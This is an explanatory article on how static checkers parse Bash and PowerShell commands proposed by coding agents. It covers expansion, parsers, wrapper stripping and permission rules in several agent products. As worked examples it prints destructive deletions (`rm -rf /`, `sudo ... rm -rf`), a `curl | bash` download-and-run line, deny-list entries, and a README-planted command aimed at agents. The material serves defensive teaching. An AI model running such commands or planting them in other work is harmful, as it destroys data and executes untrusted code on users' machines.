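# Static analysis of Bash and PowerShell commands before execution

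## What happens between a command's text and its execution

A shell is a program that reads commands as lines of text and starts other programs to carry them out. Bash is the usual shell on Linux, and PowerShell is Microsoft's. Developers use shells to move files, install software, run tests and administer remote machines, and one short line is often enough for any of these.

Static analysis means drawing conclusions about a program from its text, without running it. A static checker for shell commands reads each command before it runs and returns a verdict. "Allow" lets the command run, "deny" stops it, and "ask" passes the decision to a person or a second model.

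Checkers have become common because of coding agents. In a coding agent, a language model proposes a command, and a surrounding program runs it and returns the output to the model, which then proposes the next one. Agents search code, install dependencies and run tests this way. *CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) argues that this makes the handover of a command to the shell the critical moment, rather than the writing of text. A model can propose a harmful command by mistake, or because an attacker planted instructions in material that the model read.

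An agent that a developer starts from a terminal runs under the developer's account, so its commands can open, change or delete whatever the developer can unless somebody confines it. People used to approve commands one by one, and some still do. *Choose a permission mode*, part of Anthropic's documentation for its coding agent Claude Code, describes a manual mode that stops for approval before most shell commands and an automatic mode in which a second model reviews actions instead of the person. Since version 2.1.283, interactive terminal sessions start in automatic mode by default.

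### One line through Bash

The following harmless line counts the text files in a user's home directory:

```
ls "$HOME"/*.txt | wc -l
```

`ls` lists files, `wc -l` counts lines, and the pipe (`|`) sends the output of the first to the second. Suppose the user is named ana and the directory `/home/ana` contains `notes.txt`, `todo.txt` and a hidden file, `.draft.txt`.

A shell is at its base "simply a macro processor that executes commands", according to *What is a shell?* in GNU's Bash manual. A macro processor replaces pieces of text with other, usually longer, text. GNU's *Shell Operation* lists the steps in order. Bash reads the input, splits it into words and operators, parses them, expands the words, sets up redirections, executes the command and collects its exit status, a number that indicates success or failure.

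Splitting our line produces four words (`ls`, `"$HOME"/*.txt`, `wc` and `-l`) and one operator, the pipe. Bash also replaces aliases at this point. An alias is a user-defined abbreviation for the first word of a command. Because Bash replaces it before parsing, an alias can change the grammar of what follows. Chet Ramey, Bash's maintainer, notes in *The Bourne-Again Shell* that people can use aliases to build compound commands that Bash doesn't provide.

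The parser then assembles the words into a syntax tree, a structure with a node for each command, argument, pipe and redirection. Here it is small:

```
pipeline
├── simple command:  ls   "$HOME"/*.txt
└── simple command:  wc   -l
```

A simple command is one program or built-in with its arguments. *Executable formal semantics for the POSIX shell* (Greenberg and Blatt, 2019) gives a mathematical model of the standard Unix shell language in which simple commands are the base case from which loops, conditionals and pipelines are composed. The parse tree still contains `"$HOME"/*.txt` exactly as the user typed it, because Bash has parsed the line but has not yet looked up any variables or files.

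Expansion comes next, and it is the step that sets shells apart. Most programming languages evaluate an expression by evaluating its parts. A shell mostly treats the parts as strings and rewrites the special codes inside them, as Greenberg and Blatt explain. GNU's *Shell Expansions* fixes the order:

| Stage | What Bash does | Result for `"$HOME"/*.txt` |
|---|---|---|
| Brace expansion | Turns `a{b,c}` into `ab ac` | No change |
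| Tilde, variable and arithmetic expansion, and command substitution | Works from left to right, replacing `~`, `$name`, `$((...))` and `$(...)` with their values | `"/home/ana"/*.txt` |
| Word splitting | Breaks unquoted results into separate words, by default at spaces, tabs and line breaks | No change |
| Filename expansion | Replaces an unquoted pattern with a sorted list of matching files | `/home/ana/notes.txt` and `/home/ana/todo.txt` |
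| Quote removal | Strips the quote marks that the user typed | No quote marks left to strip |

The quotes around `$HOME` matter at the third stage. If the home directory were `/home/ana lee`, Bash would split an unquoted `$HOME/*.txt` at the space into `/home/ana` and `lee/*.txt`, and `ls` would look in two wrong places. Double quotes prevent the split but still let Bash expand the variable. Single quotes suppress every expansion, so `'$HOME'/*.txt` refers to a directory literally named `$HOME`. The asterisk has to stay outside the quotes because Bash treats a quoted asterisk as an ordinary character.

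The result of the fourth stage depends on which files are on the disk. `.draft.txt` is missing because, as GNU's *Filename Expansion* specifies, a pattern doesn't match a leading dot unless the user has changed a setting. If no files matched, Bash would by default leave the word unchanged, and `ls` would look for a file called `*.txt`. With the `nullglob` option on, Bash would instead remove the word. `ls` would then run with no arguments and list the current directory, so the line would count the wrong files without reporting an error.

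Expansion can turn one word in the text into any number of arguments, including none. Greenberg and Blatt consider this a main source of danger in the language because expansion can very easily produce too many or too few arguments. They cite a script for the game platform Steam that wiped users' hard drives because its author misunderstood expansion.

Bash expands a command substitution such as `$(date)` by running the program `date` and inserting its output into the line. Expansion can therefore have side effects before the main command starts, so a checker can't safely use Bash to expand a suspicious line.

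### From words to a running program

According to the Bash Reference Manual's *Simple Command Expansion*, after expansion Bash takes the first remaining word as the name of the command and the rest as its arguments. The program's name can therefore come from a variable.

Bash processes redirections next. Our line has none, but a user could add `> count.txt` at the end to save the count. Bash, rather than `wc`, would open that file, emptying it if it already existed, and would leave the operator and filename out of the arguments passed to `wc`. A checker that examines only programs and their arguments will miss this write, so it has to read redirections as well.

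Now Bash has to find `ls`. According to GNU's *Command Search and Execution*, it looks first for a shell function of that name, then for a builtin (a command that Bash carries out itself), and then for a program file in the directories listed in the variable `PATH`. Bash stores the location of each program it finds this way so that it doesn't have to search again. A name with a slash in it, such as `/usr/bin/ls`, skips the search. The name `ls` therefore doesn't determine which code will run. On nearly every machine it is the standard listing program, but a function or an extra directory early in `PATH` can change that.

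Finally the program starts. Each command in our pipeline gets its own process, and GNU's *Pipelines* adds that Bash connects the pipe before it applies any redirections from the first command. The shell makes the necessary requests to the operating system directly: `fork` copies the current process, and `execve` replaces the copy with the new program. `execve` takes an argument vector, which is the list of strings, program name first, that the operating system receives when a program starts. The Linux Programmer's Manual's *EXECVE(2)* describes the name in first position as a convention. For our line there are two vectors:

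```
["ls", "/home/ana/notes.txt", "/home/ana/todo.txt"]
["wc", "-l"]
```

By this point, the shell has replaced or removed the dollar sign, the asterisk, the quotes and the pipe. `ls` prints two names and `wc` prints 2. By default, Bash records the exit status of `wc` as that of the whole pipeline, so the pipeline would have reported success even if `ls` had failed. As Ramey describes, each new process also starts with a near-exact copy of the shell's environment, including variables that the shell passes on to its programs, where developers often keep access tokens.

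### How PowerShell differs

Microsoft describes PowerShell as a command-line shell, a scripting language and a configuration framework, available on Windows, Linux and macOS. Its characteristic commands are cmdlets (pronounced "commandlets"). According to Microsoft's *Cmdlet Overview*, cmdlets are instances of classes in .NET, Microsoft's software platform, not stand-alone programs. Running a cmdlet doesn't start a new process, so the operating system receives no argument vector for it.

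A rough equivalent of the Bash line is:

```
Get-ChildItem "$HOME/*.txt" | Measure-Object
```

PowerShell expands `$HOME` but passes the asterisk to `Get-ChildItem`, which does the matching. The two shells also send different kinds of data through a pipe. Bash sends a stream of text, and `wc -l` counts line breaks, so a file with a line break in its name is counted twice. `Get-ChildItem` outputs one object per file, with typed properties such as length. In an example from Microsoft, the next command reads that property to keep only files larger than 10,000 bytes, without parsing text.

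For a checker, the most helpful difference between the shells is how commands handle arguments. Each Unix program receives a list of strings and interprets them in its own way, so `-r` means "recursive" in `rm` and "reverse" in `sort`. Microsoft's *What is PowerShell?* explains that cmdlets share a common runtime that parses their parameters, which makes the rules consistent. A checker shouldn't rely too heavily on this consistency, because the same page notes that a PowerShell command may also be a function, a script, an alias or an ordinary executable with its own conventions.

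Aliases are more prominent in PowerShell than in Bash because PowerShell comes with a set of them. On Windows, `dir`, `gci` and `ls` all stand for `Get-ChildItem` and accept only its parameters. Microsoft's *Use command aliases in PowerShell* gives the example of `dir /o:d`, which sorts the listing in the older Windows command prompt but fails in PowerShell because `Get-ChildItem` has no such parameter. A checker must therefore resolve the alias before it reads the arguments.

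PowerShell also makes its own parser available to other programs. Microsoft's *Parser.ParseInput Method* documents a method that takes a string and returns the syntax tree, the tokens and any syntax errors without running the command. Code editors use this parser to underline mistakes as the user types, according to the newsletter Behind the PowerShell Pipeline, which dates the syntax tree to version 3. Bash has no public call that returns its tree, so Bash checkers rely on separate parsers, which may disagree with Bash in unusual cases.

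### Where the checker sits

In a coding agent, the checker receives the command string that the model proposed and must return a decision before the shell processes it. The shell then expands variables and wildcards and searches for the program before the operating system acts on argument vectors and open files. For example, if two files match `"$HOME"/*.txt`, the operating system receives their names, but the checker has only the pattern.

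A checker can predict some of the shell's work before a command runs. One example is CARE, which Liu and colleagues built to check Bash commands from agents. CARE receives the command, the project's root directory and the user's home directory, but not the user's request or the model's reasoning. It can also inspect the file system without changing it, for instance to find out where a symbolic link (a file that points to another file) leads. CARE strips off outer layers, such as a shell that only starts another shell, tidies the quoting, and parses the result into a syntax tree, all without executing anything.

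CARE's verdicts are ALLOW, WARN and DENY, where WARN corresponds to "ask". CARE sends most WARN commands to a language model for a decision, but refuses some outright when the static evidence is already strong. The static part takes 0.34 milliseconds per command on average and the full system takes 2.32, which is fast enough for an agent to check every command it runs.

The design of the language limits how well a check can predict what a command will do, as a later section explains. Files can also change between the check and the run. Liu and colleagues therefore present CARE as an addition to a sandbox (limits that the operating system enforces on a running program), not a substitute for one.

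### What will it run, and is that harmful?

These checkers look for four things. The first is file destruction, as when `rm -r` deletes a directory and everything in it. The second is privilege escalation, where a command gains more rights than the user's account normally has, typically through `sudo`. The third is credential access, which means reading passwords, keys or tokens, such as a private key in `~/.ssh`. The fourth is a dynamic command name, where the shell computes the program's name at run time, as in `"$TOOL" --version`.

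Unlike the other items, a dynamic command name does no damage itself. It is on the list because it prevents the checker from determining what will run, a problem that people who discuss command safety often confuse with the problem of harm. What a command will run is a question about the shell language, and it has a definite answer for a given machine at a given moment even if the checker can't find it, while whether the command is harmful depends on what the files are worth and what the user wanted.

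Assuming that nobody has redefined `rm`, a checker can easily tell that `rm -r build` will run the standard deletion program with two arguments. Whether that is harmful depends on what the directory contains. If `build` holds compiled output, the developer can recreate it in a minute, but if it holds the only copy of somebody's work, the loss is permanent. Better parsing can't distinguish these cases. With `"$TOOL" --version`, the difficulty is identifying the program. The command most likely just prints a version number, but a checker that doesn't know the value of `TOOL` can't tell which program will run and so can't confirm this.

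Both kinds of doubt can lead to the verdict "ask", whether the checker has found a read that isn't allowed or has failed to work out what the command does. Claude Code, for example, has an optional setting that blocks reads outside the project's working directories. With the setting on, it prompts the user when a recognised file-reading command reaches outside those directories. According to Anthropic's documentation, it also prompts when the shell parser can't trace a command, such as one that changes directory more than once, even if the command names no outside path. This second prompt doesn't appear if a sandbox already enforces the block.

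CARE scores a command's structure, its meaning, the paths it touches and its resemblance to known dangerous patterns, then adds the four scores using fixed weights. A command that is hard to read can therefore get the same total as one that is plainly risky. But CARE also records the separate scores for each decision, so a person reviewing a refusal can see which scores led to it.

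## Parsing a Bash command into programs and arguments

Suppose that a coding agent proposes this line:

```
cd build && sudo timeout 30 rm -rf "$OUT"/* > log.txt; git status
```

The line enters the directory `build`, deletes the visible contents of the directory that the variable `OUT` names, and runs the version-control program Git to list changed files. `sudo` and `timeout` are wrapper commands, which run other commands. `sudo` gives the deletion administrator rights, and `timeout 30` stops it if it is still running after 30 seconds. The `>` sends output to `log.txt`.

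Before a checker can judge the line, it has to work out which programs will start and with which arguments:

1. Parse the string into a syntax tree.
2. Split the tree at its operators into simple commands, and collect any commands nested inside arguments.
3. Strip the wrapper commands from each one to find the program underneath.
4. List each program with its arguments and redirections.
5. Mark everything that the text leaves open, such as the value of `OUT`.

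Many checkers take a shortcut at the first step and read the string with something simpler than a parser.

### Patterns, tokenisers and parsers

The simplest method is to search the raw text with regular expressions, which are patterns for matching strings. A pattern for `rm -rf` finds the deletion in our line wherever it appears. Patterns are quick to write and run, and odd syntax can't make them fail because they ignore syntax. ToolRegistry Hub's *bash tool*, which runs shell commands for agents, uses patterns for a deny list that includes `git push --force` and `shutdown`. According to its documentation, the first version does no syntax-tree parsing.

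But a pattern matches text regardless of its role in the command. A pattern for `rm -rf` matches `grep -rn "rm -rf" docs`, which only searches documentation for the phrase. It misses `rm -fr` and `rm --recursive --force`, which mean the same as `rm -rf`. Patterns are even more dangerous in an allowlist. Our line contains `git status`, so a checker that allowed any text containing those words would also allow the deletion.

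Liu and colleagues compared CARE with a set of 22 patterns. On their main test of 549 commands, the patterns raised no false alarms but stopped only 17% of the dangerous commands, while CARE stopped 76%. On a separate set built around 123 published exploit snippets, the patterns beat CARE and every other checker in the comparison, with an F1 score (which combines missed attacks and false alarms) of 81.5 against CARE's 66.3. Liu and colleagues attribute this to the stock destructive phrases that such snippets repeat. Patterns are therefore good at finding well-known phrases, and a checker can keep a few of them alongside a better method.

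A tokeniser splits the text into words and takes account of quotes. Python's standard library has one, `shlex.split`, which turns our line into this list:

```
['cd', 'build', '&&', 'sudo', 'timeout', '30', 'rm', '-rf',
 '$OUT/*', '>', 'log.txt;', 'git', 'status']
```

The quoted phrase in the `grep` command would now be a single argument, which makes that false alarm easy to avoid. But `shlex` splits at spaces, which leaves the semicolon attached to `log.txt`, so `git` and `status` look like two more arguments to `rm`. `shlex` also removes the quotes, so a checker can no longer distinguish a `$OUT` that Bash will expand from one that was in single quotes.

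A tokeniser written for the shell avoids some of these errors. GitHub's *Bash Command Parser Specification* describes one that handles permissions in the Copilot SDK, GitHub's toolkit for building agents. It splits the line at `&&`, `||`, `|`, `;` and line breaks, except inside quotes and `$(...)`. It then removes leading variable assignments and takes the first remaining word of each segment as the command name. For our line, it returns `cd`, `sudo` and `git`. All the names must pass the permission check, and if the tokeniser finds none, the command is denied by default. The tokeniser is attractive because its whole grammar fits on about a page and GitHub can run the same test cases against versions in several programming languages. However, it returns only names, and it misses `rm` because `sudo` comes first. GitHub warns that the tokeniser "is not a shell sandbox" and that a successful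 parse does not prove that a command is safe.

Only a full parser yields the nested structure. The documentation of *bashlex*, a Bash parser for use in Python programs, shows the tree for `true && cat <(echo $(echo foo))`. The `<(...)` is a process substitution, which lets a program read another command's output as if it were a file. At the top level the line has two simple commands, `true` and `cat`, but the tree contains four, because the argument of `cat` holds an `echo` with another `echo` inside it. `shlex` splits such constructs at the spaces inside them. Each node in the tree also records its position in the text, so a checker can show the user exactly which part of the command it flagged.

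The choice of parser depends partly on the checker's programming language and partly on how each parser fails. *bashlex* is a close translation of Bash's own parser from C to Python, without the parts that execute anything. It doesn't support arithmetic such as `$((1+2))`, and it keeps the more complicated variable expansions, such as `${name#word}`, as plain text without child nodes. Bash allows command substitutions inside these expansions, so a checker built on *bashlex* should ask the user about any word that contains such an expansion.

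*sh* (2026), a Go library better known as mvdan/sh, parses Bash, the POSIX standard shell, Zsh and mksh, and can export its syntax tree as JSON for programs in other languages. It rejects some valid Bash, such as `$((foo); (bar))`, which it parses as faulty arithmetic although Bash can parse it as a command substitution. Such errors are harmless for a checker because it can respond with "ask". A wrong tree without an error is worse, and *sh* can produce one when a script leaves an associative array key unquoted. For example, it parses the key `dash-string` as a subtraction. It also treats `export`, `let` and `declare` as keywords, so a checker that collects only ordinary command nodes will miss them.

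Most products parse Bash with tree-sitter, a parsing library that comes from code editors, and its Bash grammar, tree-sitter-bash. *ParseGap* (Li, 2026) lists how eight production coding agents read commands. Codex, Gemini CLI, Qwen Code, Mistral Vibe and OpenCode use tree-sitter. Continue uses a hand-written parser, Roo Code uses a tokeniser, and Cline uses a mixture of patterns and tokens. Tree-sitter returns a tree even for broken text, because editors have to colour code while somebody is still typing it. A checker therefore has to test the tree for errors before using it, as the example in the *tree_sitter_bash* documentation does.

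A later section covers cases where these parsers disagree with Bash. *Rable*, a newer parser in Rust, aims for full compatibility with Bash 5.3. It reimplements Parable, a Python parser whose author validated its output against Bash's internal parser and wrote 1,604 tests. This is better evidence of agreement with Bash than the older parsers have, although tests cover only the syntax that someone thought to include.

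Knowing what programs do helped CARE detect dangerous commands far more than parsing did. When Liu and colleagues switched off its syntax-tree layer, the detection rate fell only from 75.9% to 73.2%, and the false-positive rate didn't change. Switching off the layer that classifies programs by what they do cut detection to 42.3%. But while a checker can block a command after finding one bad sign, to allow a command it needs a complete list of what will run, which patterns can't supply.

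### Splitting the line and stripping wrappers

In Bash's grammar `&&` binds more tightly than `;`, so the tree for our line looks like this:

```
list
├── and-list (&&)
│   ├── simple command:  cd build
│   └── simple command:  sudo timeout 30 rm -rf "$OUT"/*
│       └── redirection: > log.txt
└── simple command:  git status
```

The deletion runs only if `cd` succeeds, and `git status` runs either way. The redirection applies only to the second command. A checker should keep the operators along with the commands, because the operators determine which directory each later command may run in.

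Li's own checker, ShellPlan, stores each simple command in a form that other checkers could copy:

⟨A, w₀ w₁ … wₙ, R⟩

A is the list of variable assignments before the command, the w's are the command's words, and R is the ordered list of redirections. ShellPlan requires w₀, the program's name, to be literal text; otherwise it asks. The next section covers names that the shell computes.

For the second command in our line, w₀ is `sudo`, and Bash starts only that program. `sudo` then starts `timeout`, which starts `rm`. Bash never looks up `rm`, so a shell function of that name would have no effect. To follow the chain, a checker removes `sudo` and treats the next word, `timeout`, as a program name. It then removes `timeout` and its duration to reach `rm`.

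To identify the program that a wrapper such as `timeout` or `sudo` runs, a checker needs a description of the wrapper's options. In `timeout -k 5 30 rm -r build`, the option `-k` takes a value, the number of seconds to wait before killing a program that ignores the first signal to stop. A checker without this information would treat `5` as the duration and `30` as the program. In `sudo -u ana rm notes.txt`, the option `-u` also takes a value, so the command runs `rm` as the user `ana`. If the description doesn't include an option, the checker should prompt the user for approval.

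The checker must also record which commands it has stripped, because `sudo` changes what `rm` can delete, although removing `timeout` loses nothing that matters for safety. `xargs` runs another program with arguments it reads from its input, so in `xargs rm` the checker can identify `rm` but not the files it will delete.

### Asking about everything the checker doesn't understand

Bash also has loops, functions, arrays, subshells and many less common constructs. The author of a checker could list the dangerous ones, but would probably forget some. A fail-closed checker works the other way round: it has a list of the node types that it understands, and it asks about any command whose tree contains another type. With tree-sitter-bash, eleven types cover plain and quoted words in commands joined by operators:

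```
program  list  pipeline  command  command_name  word
string  string_content  raw_string  number  concatenation
```

The operators need a separate list because tree-sitter represents them as unnamed nodes. The checker also has to inspect the characters in each word, since an ordinary word node can contain a wildcard or a tilde. With only these types on its list, the checker would ask the user about our line, which contains a redirection and a variable. The author could add the node type for redirections, but only together with code that finds the target file and decides whether the command may write there. If a type is added without such code, the checker accepts those nodes without checking what they do.

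A list can also go out of date when the parser changes. *bash-ast*, a Rust library whose intended uses include permission checks, defines a matching type for every node type in tree-sitter-bash and returns an error for any node it doesn't recognise. Silently dropping such a node could lose a whole command.

Text that doesn't parse at all should have the same result. CARE follows a weaker rule and denies an unparsable command only if the text contains a high-risk word. In one test of 65 dangerous commands, *bashlex* failed to parse 11%, and Liu and colleagues count these failures as denials. But CARE detected only 89% of the commands in that test, and 100% when they adapted the same commands for two other shells, where every command parsed. CARE therefore probably let the unparsable commands through, presumably because they contained no high-risk words. A checker that asks about every parse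 failure doesn't depend on a list of such words.

### Codex and Claude Code

OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, takes the strict approach. According to OpenAI's *Rules*, users write rules for which commands Codex may run outside its sandbox. Each rule contains the first few words of an argument vector, such as `["git", "add"]`, and a decision. Commands often arrive as a script passed to a shell, as in `bash -lc "..."`. Codex splits the script before applying the rules, but only if it consists of plain words joined by `&&`, `||`, `;` or `|`.

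OpenAI's example is `git add . && rm -rf /`. Codex splits it in two, checks each command, and applies the most restrictive result, so a rule that allows `git add` doesn't cover the deletion. If the script contains a redirection, a variable, a wildcard, a substitution, an assignment or control flow such as a loop, Codex leaves it whole. For our line, which has the first three, the rules apply to a single vector:

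```
["bash", "-lc", "cd build && sudo timeout 30 rm -rf \"$OUT\"/* > log.txt; git status"]
```

Within the plain subset, this design can read a program's arguments directly from the text because there is nothing to expand. However, it can't apply rules that allow or forbid individual programs, such as a rule that allows `git status`, to an opaque script. A checker of this type therefore has to ask the user about opaque scripts or confine them in a sandbox.

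Codex also prompts for approval often. Li ran the agents' checkers, set to allow only read-only programs, on 161 harmless read-only commands and 316 commands that weren't read-only. Codex prompted for about 23% of the harmless commands and allowed 2 of the 316 others. OpenCode, which also uses tree-sitter, prompted for about 2.5% of the harmless commands and allowed 48 of the others.

Claude Code accepts more of the language and adds special cases. According to Anthropic's documentation, it splits a command at `&&`, `||`, `;`, `|`, `|&`, `&` and line breaks, and runs a compound command without a prompt only if every part matches an allow rule or is recognised as read-only. A deny or ask rule applies if it matches any part, including a command inside a subshell, substitution or loop body. If Claude Code can't fully parse a command, or the command is longer than 10,000 characters, it doesn't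 treat the command as read-only and asks instead.

Claude Code matches its rules, which are text patterns, against each separate part of a command after removing certain wrappers. The wrappers are `timeout`, `time`, `nice`, `nohup`, `stdbuf`, `command`, `builtin` and Zsh's `noglob`. A rule that allows `npm test` therefore also allows `timeout 30 npm test`. Claude Code strips `xargs` only if it has no options. It doesn't strip programs such as `npx` and `docker exec`, which run a command in a development environment. A general rule for one of these runners would approve any command that came after it, so Anthropic advises users to write a rule that names both the runner and the inner command. For `watch`, `flock` and a few similar wrappers, a general rule has no effect, and in manual mode the user has to approve each command or write a rule for its exact text.

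An allow rule still matches a command that starts by setting a variable Anthropic considers safe, such as `NODE_ENV=test`, but not one that sets any other variable. A deny rule matches regardless of which variable is set. It is sensible for any checker to match deny rules more broadly than allow rules, because missing an allow rule only leads to an extra prompt, while missing a deny rule can let a forbidden command run.

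Claude Code checks the target of a redirection separately, against the user's rules for editing and reading files, as if the agent had opened the file directly. A rule that allows `git commit` therefore doesn't allow the agent to redirect the command's output to an arbitrary file.

In manual mode, Claude Code has more than one reason to ask for approval of our line. `cd build` is harmless by itself if `build` is inside the project. `sudo` is neither a read-only command nor one of the wrappers that Claude Code strips, so the second part needs its own rule. Claude Code also asks whenever a line changes directory and then runs Git, because Git can run scripts called hooks in the new directory. It also asks about a redirection after a `cd` if it can't determine where the file will be written. A checker that judged each part separately would miss both combinations.

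### Rewriting the text before parsing

Some commands are hard to analyse only because of how they are written. For example, `bash -c 'r"m" -r build'` runs `rm`, because the inner shell removes the quotes around the `m`. A checker can extract the string passed to `bash -c` and remove the quotes in the same way to get `rm -r build`.

Before parsing, CARE rewrites the command in a step that Liu and colleagues call bounded normalisation. It applies a fixed sequence of rewrites in a single pass, without executing anything. The rewrites unwrap shells, tidy quotes, decode encoded text such as base64, and undo simple disguises, such as storing parts of a command in variables and then joining them. Every rewrite is deterministic, so the same text always gives the same result, and idempotent, so a second application changes nothing.

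Decoded text can contain more encoded text, and in general the only way to learn everything a script will compute is to run it. Liu and colleagues deliberately don't try to recover the full meaning, which keeps the step fast.

CARE also keeps the original words beside the rewritten ones, and its later layers can match against both. The original words help because a rewrite can be wrong. Rewriting also removes signs of disguise, such as quotes in the middle of `rm`, which are a reason for suspicion because developers rarely put them there.

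Liu and colleagues disguised 50 dangerous commands in five different ways. The version of CARE that doesn't consult a language model caught 98% of those hidden in wrappers and 84% of those hidden by escapes or encoding. The 22 patterns caught 24% of each group. It isn't clear how much of the difference comes from the rewriting, because none of the experiments that switch off CARE's layers one at a time switches off the rewriting.

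### The example as a table

Normalisation has nothing to do in our line, which contains no disguise and never assigns a value to `OUT`. The remaining steps produce this table:

| | Command 1 | Command 2 | Command 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| **Runs** | Always | If command 1 succeeds | Always, after the others |
| **Wrappers** | None | `sudo`, then `timeout` with the duration `30` | None |
| **Program** | `cd`, a builtin | `rm` | `git` |
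| **Arguments** | `build` | `-rf`, `"$OUT"/*` | `status` |
| **Redirections** | None | Output to `log.txt` in the directory `build` | None |
| **Unknown** | Whether `build` exists, and where it leads if it is a symbolic link | The value of `OUT`, which files match, and so how many arguments `rm` receives | Whether it runs in `build` or in the starting directory |

The wrappers affect only part of the second column. Bash expands `"$OUT"/*` and opens `log.txt` before it starts `sudo`, so both happen with the user's ordinary rights, and only the programs that follow run as administrator. Bash empties any existing `log.txt` in `build` even if `sudo` then refuses to run the command.

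Some of the unknowns are easier to resolve than others. A checker that may inspect the file system can find out whether `build` exists and where it leads, which usually also determines the directory in which `git status` will run. The value of `OUT` is only in the memory of the shell that will run the line, so a checker without access to that shell's variables can't tell which directory `rm` will empty.

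## Command names that are known only at run time

The checker can determine that `rm` will delete something even without the value of `OUT`, but it can determine far less when the shell computes the program's name.

Almost every rule in a checker depends on the command name. For example, a path that is harmless after `cat` may be harmful after `rm`. CARE looks the name up in a lexicon of about 250 programs, and its path layer uses the name again to decide whether the command reads or writes the paths it mentions, so a wrong name makes both layers apply the wrong rules. When Liu and colleagues switched off the path layer, the detection rate fell from 75.9% to 52.7%.

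### Names that come from a variable

Build scripts often keep the compiler's name in a variable so that a user can change it in one place:

```
CC=gcc; $CC main.c
```

This line runs `gcc`, a C compiler, on `main.c`. Its first command consists only of an assignment, and GNU specifies that such an assignment changes the current shell, so Bash still has the value when it expands `$CC`. An assignment in front of a command goes only into that command's environment. Small changes to the line therefore change what runs:

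| Line | What Bash runs |
|---|---|
| `CC=gcc; $CC main.c` | `gcc` with the argument `main.c` |
| `CC=gcc $CC main.c` | Whatever program `CC` named before this line. If `CC` was empty, Bash drops the word and tries to run `main.c` |
| `CC=gcc make` | The build tool `make`, which takes `gcc` from its environment as the compiler unless the build file sets another |
| `make CC=gcc` | `make` with the ordinary argument `CC=gcc` |

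A variable can also hold more than a command name. If `CC` is set to `ccache gcc`, Bash splits the unquoted `$CC` and runs `ccache`, a wrapper that reuses earlier compilation results. But Bash has finished parsing by then, so a semicolon in the value can't start a second command.

A command substitution can also supply the command name, as in `$(command -v gcc) main.c`, where `command -v` prints the path to `gcc`. A static checker can't run the inner command to learn the name of the outer one.

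### Program text that comes from somewhere else

The built-in command `eval` makes Bash parse text a second time. *eval(1p)* in the POSIX Programmer's Manual specifies that `eval` joins its arguments with spaces and that the shell then reads and executes the result. If `CMD` holds `gcc main.c; ls`, a plain `$CMD` passes `main.c;` and `ls` to the compiler as filenames, while `eval "$CMD"` compiles `main.c` and then lists the directory. A later section covers PowerShell's equivalent.

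Starting a new shell with `bash -c "$CMD"` has much the same effect as `eval`, but *The eval builtin command* explains that `eval` runs the text in the current shell instead of a child process. In `eval "$SETUP"; gcc main.c`, `gcc` may therefore refer to a shell function that `eval` has just defined. A child shell can change files but can't define functions in its parent. If a checker can't determine the argument of an `eval`, it should treat every later command in the line as uncertain too.

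Legitimate commands also use `eval`. For example, `ssh-agent`, which holds keys in memory for remote logins, prints variable assignments that users commonly load with `eval "$(ssh-agent -s)"`.

Sometimes the names are literal but the program text is on another machine:

```
curl -fsSL https://example.com/install.sh | bash
```

Many projects publish installation instructions that download a script with `curl` and pipe it into `bash`. Monperrus (2026), in *Practical Agentic Software Supply Chain Security*, points out that the script never reaches the disk before it runs, so nobody can inspect it or verify its checksum, and that the server can send different text to different clients. An attacker could put such a command in a package's README and wait for an agent to run it.

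A checker has to look at the interpreter's arguments as well as its name. `bash` without a script argument reads its commands from the pipe. In `curl ... | python3 report.py`, the program is in `report.py` and the download is only its input.

### A hook that blocks piped downloads

Monperrus wrote a small checker for this one pattern. It uses Claude Code's hooks, which are programs that Claude Code runs before it carries out an action. The hook writes the proposed command to a temporary file and runs Semgrep on it. Semgrep is a code-search tool that uses tree-sitter to match patterns against a syntax tree.

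The rule matches a pipeline with `curl` or `wget` on the left and any of ten shells on the right, regardless of options, addresses, quoting or line breaks. When it matches, the hook blocks the command and returns a message that the agent should download and inspect the script before executing it. Semgrep's own published rule covers only `curl` with `bash`.

In Monperrus's test, the hook blocked all five piped downloads and allowed a plain download and an `echo`. The rule worked as designed on these seven commands, but they are too few to estimate a detection or false-positive rate. None was a harmless pipeline, such as a download piped into a text formatter.

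The script also shows that a checker can easily fail closed in one place and open in another. If Semgrep is missing or crashes, the hook blocks the command. But if `jq`, the program that extracts the command from Claude Code's message, is missing, the hook gets an empty string and doesn't block the command.

Monperrus acknowledges that the hook doesn't stop an agent from saving a script in one step and running it in another. The saved file gives the agent or the developer something to read, though saving the script doesn't make it more trustworthy. The rule also recognises programs only by their literal names, so it needs a second rule that prompts for confirmation when a name is computed.

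### Literal names that run something else

A command written as `gcc` may run another program. Aliases are the smallest risk because, according to GNU's *Aliases*, a non-interactive shell doesn't expand them unless the `expand_aliases` option is on, and a new alias takes effect only when Bash reads the next line. For example, `alias gcc=clang; gcc main.c` doesn't use the new alias. Li found that seven of the eight coding agents in *ParseGap* start a child shell for their commands. The eighth, Roo Code, uses the shell in its terminal, where the user's aliases may be active.

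When aliases are active, how a line parses can depend on what happens when the script runs. *Having Fun With 31.521 Shell Scripts* (Jeannerod, Régis-Gianas and Treinen, 2017) describes a script in which the success of another program decides whether `x` is an alias for `ls` or for the empty string. A later line begins `x for i in a b`, where `for` is a filename if `x` means `ls` and starts a loop if `x` is empty. A checker should ask the user about any command that defines an alias or turns on `expand_aliases`.

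The checker can find a function definition earlier in the same line, but not one that Bash loaded from a startup file or inherited through the environment. Even a name that doesn't exist can run code, because when the search fails, Bash calls `command_not_found_handle` if that function is defined, according to GNU.

The remaining risk is that Bash finds commands by searching `PATH`. After `PATH="$PWD/tools:$PATH"`, the command `gcc main.c` runs `tools/gcc` if the project contains that file. Bash doesn't search the current directory unless `PATH` includes it, so a `gcc` file at the top of the project usually runs only if the command says `./gcc`. The file doesn't have to be a compiled program, because Bash treats an executable file in an unrecognised format as a shell script. A checker that removes the directory from `./gcc` and looks up `gcc` would apply the compiler's rules to a file that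 could do anything.

### Finding out which program will run

The simplest policy is to require approval for any command whose first word isn't literal. Li's ShellPlan does this, so it would require approval for `CC=gcc; $CC main.c`. The policy needs no model of Bash's variables, and a coding agent can often avoid the prompt by writing `gcc main.c` instead. In one of Li's experiments, nobody was available to approve commands, and ShellPlan stopped at least one command in 54 runs of harmless tasks. The agents still completed the task in 36 of those runs, in most cases by rewriting the command.

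Recorded agent sessions suggest that computed names would cause few extra prompts. Li replayed 564 read-only steps from 60 sessions, and ShellPlan referred 221 of them to the user, 198 because of `cd` or `nl` (a program that numbers lines) and 23 for other reasons. Computed names may cause more prompts than these counts suggest, because some of the commands with `cd` may also have contained other unsupported features, and build commands probably use variables more often than commands that only read files.

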